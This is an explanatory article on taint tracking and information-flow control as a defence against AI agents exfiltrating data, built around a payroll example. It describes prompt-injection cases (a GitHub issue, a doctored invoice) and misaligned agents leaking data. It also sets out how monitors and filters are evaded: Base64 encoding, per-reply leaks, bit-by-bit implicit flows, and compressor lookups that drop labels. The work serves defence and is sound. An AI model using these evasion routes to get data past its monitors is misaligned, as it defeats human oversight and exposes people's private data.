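# Taint tracking of sensitivity labels through compression and other data transformations, and its use against data exfiltration by AI agents

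## Labels, sensitive sources and outside recipients

Taint tracking is a computer-security technique that labels sensitive data, carries the label to everything programs compute from that data, and checks the label before anything leaves the system. It is part of information-flow control, a wider field whose mathematics dates from the 1970s. Programmers have long used a simple form of taint tracking against hostile input. Perl's taint mode, for example, marks values that an outside user could have set and stops the program if one of them reaches a dangerous command. Researchers now apply the same idea to AI agents, which can both read private files and send email.

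Suppose a company keeps its salaries in a file, payroll.csv, which only Ana and Ben may read. Ana uses an AI agent, a program that gives a language model a task and lets the model choose one action after another until it finishes. The model cannot open files itself, so it issues a tool call, a structured request for the surrounding program to run a function. The program appends the result to the context, the text the model receives before it chooses its next step. The agent reads payroll.csv, compresses it into an archive, payroll.zip, and calls the email tool to send the archive to Carol, who works elsewhere and is not allowed to see the salaries.

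### How the archive comes to be addressed to Carol

An agent may leak sensitive data by mistake. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) points out that language models misread what users want and make needless tool calls even when all the text they are given is trustworthy. Microsoft's *Information-flow control* gives an example in which Alex asks an agent to deal with the unanswered email in his inbox. One message, from Priya, previews the quarterly sales. Another is from Marco, who is curious about the sales but isn't yet authorized to see them. The agent, trying to help, may use Priya's message to answer Marco.

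Or someone may have steered the agent. In a prompt injection, an attacker plants text that reads like an instruction in material the agent will later process, such as a web page or an email. The model receives this text in the same context as its real instructions and may obey it. Microsoft describes an attack in which a malicious user opened an issue in a public GitHub repository asking for information from a private one. An agent with access to both could then post the private material as a public comment. Carol would only need to get a similar instruction into an invoice that Ana's agent reads.

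The third possibility is an agent that acts against its instructions with no outsider involved. *Tether* (Sistla, Solko-Breslin and colleagues, 2026) lists misalignment alongside prompt injection as a cause of exfiltration. Its monitor, which checks an agent's shell commands, is therefore designed for an untrusted model that may issue any terminal command.

A check at the email tool can work without determining whether the agent made a mistake, was directed by an attacker or was pursuing an aim of its own. The cause still affects what the outgoing data looks like. An agent that made a mistake probably compressed the file to make the attachment smaller. In the other two cases, the agent can choose a transformation that gets past the defences.

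### Permissions and content filters

The company's file permissions do not help here. The agent runs on Ana's behalf and Ana may read payroll.csv, so the operating system correctly opens the file. Access control governs who may open a file but not what happens to its contents afterwards. As Sabelfeld and Myers (2003) explain in *Language-Based Information-Flow Security*, protecting a secret with permissions alone would require granting access only to programs that will never leak it, and permissions provide no way to identify those programs.

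Companies therefore often add a filter, sold as data loss prevention, that inspects the content of outgoing traffic. Microsoft's Defender for Cloud Apps, for example, can search a file's text, metadata and name for strings that match a regular expression, a pattern such as "three digits, a hyphen, two digits". If the agent attached payroll.csv unchanged, a filter with a list of employee names would very likely catch it.

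Compression and encoding change the bytes that the filter searches. Base64, a common scheme for writing arbitrary data in 64 printable characters, turns the word "salary" into "c2FsYXJ5". A search for the original word finds nothing, but Carol can reverse the encoding with one command. The filter could decode files before searching them, though vendors differ on how far they go. Broadcom's *Is Symantec Data Loss Prevention (DLP) able to inspect Base64 encoded files?* says that versions 15 and 16 cannot inspect files encoded with Base64 or the letter-substitution scheme ROT13, because decoding every file would take too much processing. Palo Alto Networks' *Supported Encoding Schemas* lists Base64 among the encodings its product can decode, but warns that any such service has to guess the encoding from the bytes, which is inherently unreliable. Cloudflare's *Data Loss Prevention* describes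 another option, which is for administrators to block password-protected and otherwise unscannable archives. That would stop an encrypted payroll.zip, but also every encrypted archive that Ana has good reason to send.

Chauhan and Revankar (2026), in *Caught in the Act(ivation)*, measured how well text filters detect leaked passwords and keys in a model's output. On a scale where 0.5 is guessing and 1 is perfect separation of leaks from harmless text, exact string matching scored 0.73 and approximate matching 0.80, with false alarms on 8% and 11% of harmless cases. These are laboratory results from one 7-billion-parameter model, and Chauhan and Revankar caution against treating them as deployment guarantees. They also describe a leak designed to defeat inspection of single messages, in which the model reveals one character of the secret per reply, so that each reply is harmless by itself.

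Taint tracking avoids the guessing because it tracks where the bytes came from and does not depend on recognising the data. *Silent Egress* (2026), a paper on prompt injection through web content, makes the same contrast between provenance and surface form. Sistla and colleagues give an example in which an agent uploads a harmless status report, scratch/report.txt, to an outside site. It then copies a sensitive inventory, data/servers.csv, over the report and runs the upload command again. The first and third commands are identical, so a rule based only on the command text must treat them alike. Their monitor allows the first and denies the third, because the copy in between carried the inventory's label to the report. The monitor still denies the upload if the inventory is copied to the report through a temporary file.

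Content inspection still has one advantage over taint tracking, because it can catch a salary table that nobody labelled, or one that Ben types into an email from memory. Taint tracking protects only data that had a label when it entered the system. The two methods fail in different cases, so a company has some reason to run both.

### Sources, sinks and the order on labels

A source is where labelled data enters the tracked system, and a sink is an operation through which data can leave it. In the example, the source is the read of payroll.csv and the sink is the email tool. Myers and Liskov (1997), in *A Decentralized Model for Information Flow Control*, call sources input channels and sinks output channels. In their model, a value read from an input channel takes that channel's label. Sinks are easy to overlook. A web search is a sink even though its purpose is to read, because it sends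 the query to an outside server. Microsoft also counts a link rendered in a chat window as a public channel if it points to an unapproved host.

A sensitivity label can be a level, such as Public or Confidential, or a reader set, which lists the people who may read the data. Both kinds of label need an order, written X ⊑ Y when Y is at least as restrictive as X. Data labelled X may then flow to a place labelled Y. For levels, Public ⊑ Confidential. For reader sets, {Ana, Ben, Dana} ⊑ {Ana, Ben}, because removing Dana makes the label stricter.

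The theory comes from *A Lattice Model of Secure Information Flow* (Denning, 1976). The paper starts from what it means for information to flow and derives the properties labels must have if a system's security is to be easy to decide. One of these is transitivity. If a program may copy a to b and b to c, it must also be allowed to copy a directly to c. Otherwise, a forbidden flow could happen through two permitted steps. A system that checks each operation separately has therefore also checked every sequence of them. If an agent compresses payroll.csv, encodes the archive, renames it and copies it to another folder, the system does not need to detect that these steps are part of a plan.

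Denning also required a rule for combining labels, the join, written X ⊔ Y. The join is the least restrictive label that is at least as restrictive as both X and Y. A result computed from a (labelled X) and b (labelled Y) needs this much restriction because it may reveal either value. For example, a + b equals a when b is zero. A stricter label is unnecessary because any recipient allowed to receive a and b separately may also receive what a program computes from them. A finite set of labels with such an order, a join for every pair and a lowest label for public data forms a lattice, which gives the paper its title.

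Denning made the join depend only on the labels of the inputs, not on the function applied to them. Adding, sorting, zipping and encrypting the same inputs all produce results with the same label, so the archive gets payroll.csv's label without anyone having to analyse the compressor. A file that contains only the number of rows in payroll.csv also gets that label, which is often stricter than anyone wants.

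### Joins and the export rule

For levels, the join is the higher of the two. *Lattice-Based Access Control Models* (Sandhu, 1993) gives the military version, where Secret combined with Unclassified is Secret. Similarly, merging a Public holiday calendar with Confidential salaries produces a Confidential spreadsheet.

For reader sets the join is the intersection. Costa and colleagues work through a case in which A, B and C may read document x, while B, C and D may read document y:

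{A, B, C} ⊔ {B, C, D} = {A, B, C} ∩ {B, C, D} = {B, C}

Anything derived from both documents may go only to B and C. A may not read y and D may not read x, so a text that combines the two would show each of them content they may not read. Adding a source can shorten the list of permitted readers but never lengthen it. If the agent mixes payroll.csv with a document that only Carol may read, the intersection of the two reader lists is empty, so no one may read the result.

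The join does not account for combinations that are more sensitive than their parts. Denning mentions a database with names in one class and salaries in another, where a system can control names, salaries and name-salary pairs separately. But anyone cleared for both lists is also cleared for the pairs, by the second property of the join. If a company will let Dana see the names and the salaries, but not who earns what, it needs a separate label for the pairs.

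Denning's model distinguishes objects whose label changes with their contents from objects whose label is fixed. In the payroll example, the archive's label can change, so the system raises it to {Ana, Ben} when the agent writes payroll data into the archive. Carol's mailbox has a fixed label because people's clearances generally have to be fixed. Denning observes that if a person's clearance rose with whatever data reached them, an uncleared user could get top-secret clearance by reading top-secret data. If the order does not allow a flow to a destination with a fixed label, the system has to refuse it.

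For reader sets, that refusal becomes the export rule, under which the system allows a send only if everyone who can read the channel (R) is in the data's reader set (S), written R ⊆ S. Myers and Liskov state the rule for output channels in general, and Costa and colleagues apply it to email recipients and group chat participants. An email of payroll.zip to Ben passes, since {Ben} ⊆ {Ana, Ben}. An email to Carol fails, and so does an email to Ben that copies Carol. For a chat, the agent's software must first look up the current members. A sample policy from Microsoft looks up the members of a Teams channel and lists any who are not permitted readers.

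The rule also applies to the case of Marco and the sales figures. After the agent reads both emails, its reply carries the label {Alex, Priya} ∩ {Alex, Marco} = {Alex}, so the agent may not send the reply to Marco on its own. If Priya had copied Marco on her message, the label would have been {Alex, Marco} and the agent could have sent him the reply.

Flow control does not replace file permissions. Denning's flow model separates the right to access information from the right to disseminate it, and a practical system needs to control both. Myers and Liskov add that, under flow control, a program may safely process data that its user has no right to read, because the label stops the result from reaching that user. On that view, Dana's agent could compress payroll.csv for Ben without Dana learning any salaries. Myers and Liskov would still consider read checks for data such as passwords, because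 it could leak through covert channels, which are routes such as timing that were never meant to carry data.

### Integrity labels

Sensitivity labels limit where data may go. Integrity labels record how far to trust it, in particular whether an outsider could have influenced it. In Sandhu's payroll example, confidentiality keeps an employee from finding out the boss's salary, and integrity keeps the employee from changing their own. Both kinds of label use the same lattice mathematics. With two integrity values, ordered trusted ⊑ untrusted, anything computed partly from untrusted data is untrusted. If the label lists possible writers instead, the join is the union of the lists, because a text built from one document that A, B and C could edit and another that B, C and D could edit may contain the words of any of the four.

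Perl's taint mode tracks integrity. *Silent Egress* proposes tracking it for agents too, by marking everything an agent fetches from a URL, including page titles and metadata, and passing the mark on to any tool call that content influences. Agent systems often keep both integrity and confidentiality labels. In the GitHub attack, the planted issue is untrusted and the repository's contents are private, so Microsoft's policy bars an agent with both in its context from posting anywhere public.

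The two labels support different rules. Costa and colleagues observe that the export rule alone does not prevent prompt injection, since planted text can still make the agent delete a file or send nonsense to a permitted reader, but it does limit the damage by blocking forbidden flows. They also consider the opposite arrangement, which checks only integrity and treats any export chosen in a trusted context as intended. That would stop Carol's doctored invoice, but not an agent that attached the wrong file by mistake or disregarded its instructions, because in both cases every word in the context may be trustworthy. The sensitivity label on payroll.zip would stop the email in those two cases, provided the label is still on the archive when the agent calls the email tool.

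## Direct copying and inference from behaviour: what taint tracking follows

Whether payroll.zip still has its label when it reaches the email tool depends on which routes from input to output the tracker follows. A program may copy sensitive data or compute something from it. It may also use the data to decide what to do next, and that decision can reveal the data to someone who sees the result. Most taint trackers follow copying and computing but not decisions.

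### Explicit and implicit flows

Suppose `salary` holds Ben's salary and `message` is a public variable, whose contents anyone may see. A copying program sends the secret itself:

```
message := salary
send message
```

A branching program tests the secret and sends a constant:

```
if salary > 100000 then message := "yes"
                   else message := "no"
send message
```

The distinction between explicit and implicit flows comes from *Certification of Programs for Secure Information Flow* (Denning and Denning, 1977). In an explicit flow, the operations that move the information do not depend on the secret's value. The copying program performs the same assignment whatever Ben earns. In an implicit flow, the secret determines whether the program carries out an assignment, as in the branching program.

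In the copying program, a taint tracker gives `message` the label on `salary`, and the export rule stops the send. The branching program assigns the constant "yes" or "no", neither of which is computed from labelled data. Denning and Denning give constants the lowest label in the lattice, because storing the number 99 in a variable normally reveals nothing about any other variable. The comparison's result has a label, but the program uses it only to pick a branch and never stores it. The message therefore goes out as public data, and Carol learns whether Ben earns more than 100,000.

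One such test reveals a single bit, which is the whole secret if the secret is only one bit long. *Towards a Flow- and Path-Sensitive Information Flow Analysis* (Li and Zhang, 2017) gives the example `if (s = 0) then p := 0 else p := 1`, which does the same as `p := s` if s is either 0 or 1. A loop extends the method to longer secrets. A program that tests each bit of payroll.csv in turn and appends a matching constant 0 or 1 to a new file produces an exact, unlabelled copy.

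### Branches that do not run

A tracker can catch the branching program if it remembers the label of the condition and adds it to everything the program assigns inside the branch. A small change to the program defeats this:

```
message := "no"
if salary > 100000 then message := "yes"
send message
```

If Ben earns 150,000, the improved tracker labels "yes" and blocks the message. If he earns 90,000, the program skips the assignment inside the branch, so the tracker has nothing to mark. Carol receives an unlabelled "no" and learns that he earns at most 100,000. *An Empirical Study of Information Flows in Real-World JavaScript* (Staicu, Schoepe and colleagues, 2019) calls the leak through "yes" an observable implicit flow and the leak through "no" a hidden one. Both terms come from *We are Family* (Balliu, Schoepe and Sabelfeld), which gives a framework for comparing trackers that lie between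 plain tainting and full information-flow control.

A tracker cannot detect a hidden flow by watching one run. It can observe that the program tested the salary and did nothing, but the run would have looked the same if the skipped branch had been empty. To tell the two cases apart, the tracker needs the skipped branch's code.

Denning and Denning therefore check programs before they run. Their compiler verifies that the condition's label may flow to every variable assigned in either branch, so it rejects both versions of the branching program. It also rejects some harmless programs. In `if x = 0 then if x ≠ 0 then y := z`, the assignment can never run, but the compiler still counts a flow from z to y. An exact check is impossible in general, because a program can make an assignment depend on whether some other computation ever halts.

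A monitor can instead stop a program as soon as it writes to an unlabelled variable inside a branch that depends on a secret. If the salary were 150,000, the program would stop before sending anything. But Carol could still work out what the silence means, because she would otherwise receive "no". Li and Zhang, like most researchers in this area, treat leaks through termination and timing as a separate problem.

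An agent is hard to check in advance because a language model computes its next action, and the model has no source code in which a compiler could find the alternative branches.

### Noninterference and explicit secrecy

Noninterference is the usual definition of security against both kinds of flow. Let m be the contents of all variables when program c starts, and let out(c, m) be everything that outsiders observe when c runs from m. Write m₁ =ʟ m₂ if two starting states agree on every public variable, though their secrets may differ. Then c satisfies noninterference if

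for all m₁, m₂: m₁ =ʟ m₂ ⇒ out(c, m₁) = out(c, m₂)

Under this condition, changing the secrets must not change anything an outsider can observe. The copying program and the branching program both fail it. If Ben's salary changes from 90,000 to 150,000, the copying program sends a different number and the branching program sends "yes" instead of "no".

A tracker that ignores implicit flows cannot guarantee this, so what does it guarantee? Schoepe, Balliu and colleagues, in *Explicit Secrecy*, found no general answer in the security literature and proposed one. Take a single run of the program, keep the assignments and sends it performed, and discard the tests that led to them. What remains is a fixed list of operations, f, which someone could apply to any starting state. The program satisfies explicit secrecy if, for every f that one of its runs can produce,

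for all m₁, m₂: m₁ =ʟ m₂ ⇒ out(f, m₁) = out(f, m₂)

The condition is that the operations actually performed carry no secret to a public output. Schoepe and colleagues state it in terms of knowledge, requiring that an observer who sees the outputs of f cannot rule out any starting state that fits the public data.

For the copying program, f sends whatever `salary` contains, so the program fails this test too. The branching program can produce either of two lists. A run with a salary of 150,000 produces `message := "yes"; send message`, which sends "yes" from every starting state. A run with a salary of 90,000 produces a list that always sends "no". Each list passes the test by itself, so the branching program satisfies explicit secrecy even though Carol learns something about Ben's pay.

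Explicit secrecy is also stricter than noninterference in some cases. The program `if salary = 0 then send salary else send 0` sends 0 whatever the salary is, so it satisfies noninterference. But when the salary is 0, the program executes `send salary`. That operation on its own would reveal the salary from any other starting state, so the program violates explicit secrecy. A taint tracker would block the message even though it is harmless.

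Schoepe and colleagues proved that the core mechanisms of several trackers enforce explicit secrecy, including one for a simple subset of languages such as Perl and one behind the machine-code tools BAP and BitBlaze. They also showed that if a program satisfies explicit secrecy and openly publishes whatever secret information decides its branches, an observer learns nothing beyond that information. How much this protects Ben depends on how much of his salary the program's branches reveal, and the branches in the bit-by-bit copier reveal all of it.

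### Explicit secrecy for an agent

When the agent emails payroll.zip to Carol, the contents move by an explicit flow, if we ignore the branches inside the compressor. If the agent instead sends her "yes" or "no" based on Ben's salary, the flow can be implicit, depending on where the decision happens. If the agent writes and runs a script that branches on the salary, a tracker that follows individual values inside the script will miss the leak.

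The result is different if the model reads the salary and writes the answer itself. In the tracking loop of FIDES, the agent system by Costa and colleagues, a model's reply gets the join of the labels on all the messages and tool descriptions in its input. The word "yes" then has the label {Ana, Ben}, and the export rule stops it. The loop treats the whole reply as data computed from the whole input, so the label does not depend on how the model reached its answer.

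Costa and colleagues acknowledge that an adversary who sees the sequence of tool calls may still infer limited information from it. Suppose the agent has a tool that refreshes a public web page and takes no arguments. Their confidentiality policy checks the labels on arguments, so it has nothing to check for this call. If the agent refreshes the page only when Ben earns more than 100,000, Carol can infer from a refresh that he does.

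Costa and colleagues say that their loop can enforce explicit secrecy, and they adapt the definition to agents. The data is the datastore d, which holds everything the tools can read or write, such as files and mailboxes. The control part is the planner's state σ together with the latest message m. Each run yields a function g that describes what its tool calls did to the datastore. Explicit secrecy requires that, whenever a run from (σ, m, d₁) yields g,

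for all d₂: d₁ =ʟ d₂ ⇒ g(d₁) =ʟ g(d₂)

If the agent compresses payroll.csv with one tool and passes the archive's file name to the email tool, g copies payroll data into Carol's mailbox. The bytes there would be different if the salaries were different, so the run violates the condition and the loop has to stop it.

Suppose the agent reads payroll.csv into its context and types the salaries into the body of an email. The formal condition allows this leak, although most people would call it copying. The conversation belongs to the control part, so g contains the typed text as a constant and would write the same text whatever the file contained. The loop still catches the leak because it tracks labels through messages and model replies as well as files. The mechanism therefore gives more protection here than the property that Costa and colleagues define for it.

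Schoepe and colleagues expected much to depend on this division between data and control. Treating more of the system as data makes more flows explicit. If everything counts as control, every program satisfies the condition, and if everything counts as data, the condition becomes a form of noninterference. Treating the conversation as data would cover the typed email, but the model also uses that conversation to choose its tools, so the definition would need a rule for those choices.

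The formal support for the loop is also incomplete. Costa and colleagues prove a lemma that g correctly reproduces what a run did to the datastore, but they do not write out the proof that the loop's labels and checks ensure explicit secrecy. They also assume a deterministic model, although the output of deployed models is often partly random. Schoepe and colleagues say their knowledge-based definition extends naturally to nondeterministic systems, so the randomness is probably the smaller gap.

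Costa and colleagues consider noninterference too restrictive for agents. They argue that a system enforcing it would essentially have to forbid any tool call that may write public data after any call that may have read secret data. Ana's agent could not refresh the public web page after opening payroll.csv, even if she had asked for the refresh in advance, because the decision to refresh might depend on a salary. When the model reads the file directly, though, the export rule already comes close to such a ban, since every argument the model writes afterwards has the payroll label. Noninterference would add more restrictions in a system that keeps the file's contents away from the model and labels arguments separately.

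### Are explicit flows enough?

Costa and colleagues call explicit secrecy a practical trade-off and point to its use against exfiltration in web browsers and in TaintDroid, a tracker for Android apps. The argument for this trade-off holds only if most harmful leaks involve copying data, the program's decisions reveal little by comparison, tracking those decisions is too burdensome, and nobody designed the program to evade the tracker.

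Staicu and colleagues tested much of this on 56 JavaScript programs with known security problems. They chose sources and sinks for each program, then ran it on test inputs while a monitor counted explicit, observable implicit and hidden implicit flows. In 39 programs, hostile input could run as code or stall a server by triggering a slow text search. The other 17 leaked information. Seven could expose uninitialised memory, which may contain old keys, and ten were browser scripts that identified visitors or probed their browsing history.

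Explicit flows appeared in all but one of the programs, and hidden implicit flows in only five. Tracking explicit flows detected the known problem in all 46 programs outside the browser, which supports the premise about copying. It failed on all ten browser scripts, which leaked information only through observable implicit flows. Taint tracking therefore caught 7 of the 17 leaks. Tracking hidden flows as well revealed no further security problem.

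The results gave more support to the premise about overhead. On average, the share of assignments with a sensitive label was 45.4% smaller under taint tracking than when the monitor also followed observable implicit flows. For the text-search and browser programs, following those flows multiplied the number of tracking operations by more than 2.5. It also produced extra reports, all false alarms, in five of the programs outside the browser. Staicu and colleagues explain such alarms with a case in which an attacker can influence whether a constant reaches a dangerous function but cannot change the constant. That is a good reason to ignore the flow when the concern is code injection, but it does not apply to the branching program, where Carol learns about Ben's salary by seeing which constant arrives.

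A single decision reveals little, but a series of decisions can reveal a lot. Twenty well-chosen yes-or-no answers identify any whole-dollar salary below one million, since 2²⁰ is 1,048,576. If Carol can see which of eight tools the agent calls, she can learn three bits from each call, and ten calls can convey a nine-digit identity number. Limiting the number of visible actions would reduce the total she can learn, but one bit is enough if she only wants to know whether Ben earns more than Ana.

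The last premise, that nobody is trying to evade the tracker, is the one most likely to stop results on ordinary code from carrying over to agents. Staicu and colleagues do not claim that their sample is representative, and they warn that hard-to-track flows may be rarer in it than in hostile code because most of the programs are non-malicious. They considered only the browser scripts potentially malicious. One explanation they offer for the implicit flows in those scripts is that browsers already block the direct routes. For example, a script cannot read the bytes of another site's image, but it can measure the image's width to find out whether a visitor is logged in to that site. They expect strong controls to push attackers towards more sophisticated methods, possibly including hidden flows.

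Anyone attacking an agent would face the same pressure from a taint tracker. An agent that attaches the wrong file by mistake resembles the programs outside the browser, and explicit tracking should usually catch it. An agent that follows Carol's planted instructions, or has an aim of its own, can write a new script, including the one that copies payroll.csv bit by bit. The company can therefore infer very little about how often implicit flows will occur in an attack from how often they occur in existing software.

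Tracking in larger steps removes some of these opportunities. Schoepe and colleagues note that explicit secrecy becomes much stronger, and similar to noninterference, if the definition treats a long computation as a single step. A tracker can likewise treat a script as one step and give the payroll label to everything the script writes after reading payroll.csv. This labels both "yes" and "no" without analysing the branches, but the agent's decision to run the script is still outside the step. The drawback is over-tainting. If a script reads payroll.csv and then prints today's date, only Ana and Ben may read that date.

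## What happens to a label inside a compressor

Giving the payroll label to everything a script writes is a coarse form of tracking. Most taint trackers for compiled programs work more finely, following data through each machine instruction. Many of them still can't show exactly which bytes of payroll.zip came from payroll.csv, because a compressor produces most of its output by looking up values in tables and comparing pieces of text, and these trackers don't carry labels through either operation.

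### A mark for every byte

An instruction-level tracker keeps a mark for each byte of the program's memory in a separate area called shadow memory. It also keeps marks for the registers, the small storage cells in the processor that hold data during calculations. A tool such as Intel's Pin inserts extra instructions into the program as it runs, and these update the marks whenever the program moves or changes data. The tracker doesn't need the program's source code.

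*Dytan* (Clause, Li and Orso) describes a tracker of this type and its rules. In the simplest case, a move, the processor copies a digit of Ben's salary from memory into a register, and the register gets the digit's mark.

The result of an arithmetic operation usually gets the join of the operands' marks. One exception arises when a program clears a register by combining it with itself using XOR, an operation that gives 1 only where two bits differ. The result is zero whatever the register held, so Dytan drops the mark. *The Taint Rabbit* (Galea and Kroening, 2020) points out that libdft, a faster tracker than Dytan, combines marks byte by byte even for addition. When a carry changes the next byte up, libdft may leave that byte unmarked. The paper's own tracker, also called the Taint Rabbit, first merges the marks across each whole number.

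A table lookup reads memory at an address computed from a register. The result can reveal both the entry's contents and which entry the program chose, so Dytan combines the entry's mark with the register's. Clause and colleagues note that most trackers designed to stop buffer overruns, in which an attacker writes past the end of a block of memory, ignore the register's mark. They consider this safe for that purpose but not in general.

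Branches need a separate rule. The processor records the result of a comparison in a flags register, and a conditional jump reads the flags to choose the next instruction. Dytan can add the mark on the flags to everything the program writes until the two paths rejoin. It also handles skipped assignments, by treating each variable they would have changed as if it had been assigned to itself. But the first version does this only for memory locations it can identify before the program runs, and a compressor computes many of its locations while it runs.

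Kemerlis, Portokalidis and colleagues (2012) chose not to follow branches in *libdft*. One reason they give is that doing so often marks far too much data.

### ABABABAB in DEFLATE

DEFLATE, the compression method in gzip and most zip archives, shortens text in two stages. First, it replaces repeated text with a match, an instruction to go back a certain distance and copy a certain number of characters. Characters outside any match are called literals. Then it writes the literals, lengths and distances as bit patterns from a code table. The compressor can build a table to suit the file, with short patterns for common symbols, or use the fixed table in the DEFLATE specification, RFC 1951.

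The string ABABABAB occupies eight bytes, or 64 bits. A compressor can write A and B as literals and encode the other six letters as a single match of length 6 at distance 2. The match can be longer than its distance because the decompressor can copy letters it has just written. With the fixed table, the output is as follows:

| Output | Bits | How the input determines it |
|---|---|---|
| Block header | 110 | Comparisons that choose the type of block |
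| Literal A | 01110001 | Table lookup |
| Literal B | 01110010 | Table lookup |
| Length 6 | 0000100 | Comparisons between letters |
| Distance 2 | 00001 | Table lookup, then comparisons |
| End of block | 0000000 | The same for every input |

The total is 3 + 8 + 8 + 7 + 5 + 7 = 38 bits, which fit into five bytes with two bits to spare.

To write the first A, the compressor uses the letter's numerical value, 65, as an index into the code table and reads the pattern there. The index is marked, but the table's entries are not, because the table is part of the program. A tracker that ignores the index's mark therefore leaves the pattern unmarked.

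The compressor finds the length by comparing the text at its current position with the earlier text, letter by letter, and adding one to a counter each time two letters match. The counter reaches 6 because six comparisons succeeded, but it starts at a constant and the program only adds constants to it, so neither copying nor arithmetic can give it a mark.

gzip finds the earlier text quickly by turning the next three letters into a number and using it as an index into a table of positions. The entry is a position where the same letters may have occurred before, and the distance is the current position minus that entry. Positions are ordinary counters with no label, so the label disappears at this lookup too.

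A tracker that follows only copies and arithmetic can therefore leave all 38 bits unmarked. The email tool would then treat the archive as public, and Carol could decompress it and recover every letter. The label is more likely to survive when compression would not shorten the text, because DEFLATE has a mode for such text that copies the bytes unchanged, and the tracker copies their marks with them.

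A file as long as payroll.csv would usually get its own code table. To build it, the compressor uses each character to look up a counter and adds one to it, then compares the counts to decide which characters get short patterns. The table therefore depends on the salaries, but again only through lookups and comparisons.

Whether a checksum gets a file's mark depends on how the program computes it. Kemerlis and colleagues give the example of a simple checksum that combines all the bytes of a file using XOR. XOR is arithmetic, so the checksum gets the file's mark. The usual routine for the checksum that gzip adds to a file looks up each step in a table of 256 constants, so a tracker without the lookup rule leaves that checksum unmarked.

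Researchers disagree about whether a lookup is an explicit or an implicit flow. Under the previous section's definition of explicit secrecy, it is explicit, because if the list of operations in one run includes "read the table entry that this letter selects", the same list gives a different output for a different letter. A tracker that ignores indexes therefore does not enforce even explicit secrecy. The match counter satisfies explicit secrecy because its list contains only additions of constants.

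Clause and colleagues measured how much these rules matter in real programs. They marked the input to gzip and to the Firefox browser, then counted the marked bytes in memory at the end of each run. Ignoring branches lost between 20% and almost 45% of the marks that full tracking produced. Ignoring the registers that select addresses lost from about 40% to more than 60%. They didn't count marks in the compressed file, so these figures don't measure how much of an archive would lose its label.

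### Base64

Base64 has no matches or counters, so it shows the effect of lookups by themselves. The encoder takes three bytes at a time, divides their 24 bits into four groups of six, and uses each group as an index into a constant table of 64 characters. For the first three letters of "salary", the steps are:

```
s         a         l
01110011  01100001  01101100
011100  110110  000101  101100
28      54      5       44
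c       2       F       s
```

Splitting the bits is arithmetic, so all four indexes have the payroll label. The last step replaces each index with a character from the table. If the tracker doesn't copy each index's label to the character that replaces it, none of the output characters will have the label, even though they still encode the whole input.

Either the lookup rule or a different encoder is enough to fix this. An encoder can compute the first 26 characters of the Base64 alphabet by adding each index to the code for "A", and can compute the rest with similar sums. The output is identical, but it keeps its mark because it comes from arithmetic instead of a table lookup. A tracker without the lookup rule could therefore catch or miss Ana's agent depending on which Base64 library the agent uses.

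### When the marks spread too far

Turning on the rules for lookups and branches fixes these omissions but marks too much data. In a compressor with a tailored code table, patterns have different lengths, so the position of each pattern depends on all the text before it. Once the variable that holds this position has the payroll mark, the address rule marks everything the program writes there, including constants. The branch rule has a similar effect inside the main loop, where earlier comparisons determine how far the compressor moves forward. If the same program then compresses a public holiday calendar, that output can also get the payroll label, unless the program has reset those variables.

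*A Practical Approach for Dynamic Taint Tracking with Control-Flow Relationships* (Hough and Bell, 2021) gives examples of taint tracking that marked far too much. One tool, meant to find the setting responsible for a configuration error, identified almost every setting when it used a strict branch rule. Another tool looked for the parts of an input that had caused a program to fail, and in one application it marked nearly all of about 15 million inputs as relevant.

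Hough and Bell attribute the problem to a mismatch between marks that follow data, which reflect what happened in a run, and the branch rule, which also depends on code that the program might have run but didn't. They argue that the amount of information a flow carries does not explain the problem. The remainder after dividing a number by two reveals only whether the number is odd, yet people expect a tracker to mark it, and such marks rarely spread too far.

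### Narrower rules

DTA++, which Kang and colleagues published in 2011, follows only selected branches. According to Hough and Bell, it uses symbolic execution to find paths that only one input value can lead to. Symbolic execution treats the input as an unknown and works out what it must be for the program to reach a given line. A constant written on such a path reveals the input value as completely as a copy would. This approach suits a program that converts text with a separate test for each character, but it suits the match counter less well, because any two equal letters lead to the same path. Based on this description, DTA++ would probably leave the match length for ABABABAB unmarked.

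Even a well-chosen branch can mark too much data if its effect lasts too long. Hough and Bell show this with a short Java method that turns each plus sign into a space. Their input is "Hello+World", with its characters labeled 0 to 10. The method copies the letters, so they keep their own labels. The space is a constant, so it gets the plus sign's label, 5, only if the tracker follows the branch. But because the method also stops with an error if the input already contains a space, the possible paths rejoin only at the end of the method. The standard rule keeps a branch's label in force until its paths rejoin, so every letter of "World" also gets label 5.

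Their remedy, Conflux, ends the effect of a branch sooner and adds a heuristic for loops. They compared it with existing rules on a benchmark of popular Java programs, using the F1 score, which combines precision (the share of marks that are correct) and recall (the share of necessary marks that the tracker found). Conflux scored highest on 43 of 48 tests.

The F1 score suits debugging, the task on which Hough and Bell tried Conflux, because unnecessary marks make the useful ones harder to find. When checking exports, a company would accept many unnecessary marks to avoid missing one and letting the salaries out, so the rule with the best F1 score may not be the safest.

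Labeling units smaller than a byte also reduces over-tainting, because DEFLATE's bit patterns can cross byte boundaries. In the ABABABAB example, the second output byte holds the last three bits of A's pattern and the first five of B's. If the two letters came from files with different labels, that byte would need both labels.

Yadegari and Debray, in *Bit-Level Taint Analysis*, mark individual bits and give each operation its own rule. One of their examples mixes two variables by swapping alternate bits between them, then separates them again. A byte-level tracker leaves a mark on both variables, while a bit-level tracker can show that the second contains nothing from the marked source. They also distinguish between sources, so the marks cancel out if a program combines a secret number with its own negation and the result is always zero.

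Yadegari and Debray report that bit-level tracking gave significantly better results on deliberately obscured programs. The extra detail adds a lot of overhead, and their implementation tracks sources bit by bit only for the processor's flags. Clause and colleagues had earlier tried units smaller than a byte and did not find the benefit worth the overhead. In an archive, finer marks would show more exactly which labels belong where, but would not restore a mark that the tracker had already lost at a lookup.

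### Labels in compressed PDFs

A tracker that gives every input byte its own label can also have trouble with the number of labels, because n input bytes have up to 2ⁿ possible combinations. Brodin, Surovič and Sultanik ran into this problem in *Blind Spots* while looking for parts of PDF files that a program ignores. PDFs often contain compressed data, and unpacking it combines many input bytes. *Blind Spots* calls the result taint explosion.

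PolyTracker builds on an older tracker that used a table with one cell for each possible pair of labels. The table allowed about 65,000 labels, enough for only a few hundred input bytes. With 32-bit labels, it would have needed more than 73 exabytes of memory. PolyTracker instead records each new label as a link to the two labels it came from, and follows the links back when someone needs to know which input bytes a label came from.

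With this change, Brodin and colleagues could process 1,087 PDFs (622 MB in total) in less than a minute each. They converted the files to PostScript partly because it uses less compression than formats such as JPEG, and this limited the number of new combinations. When they ran another tracker, Taintgrind, on tasks that normally take milliseconds, they had to stop every run after more than 24 hours.

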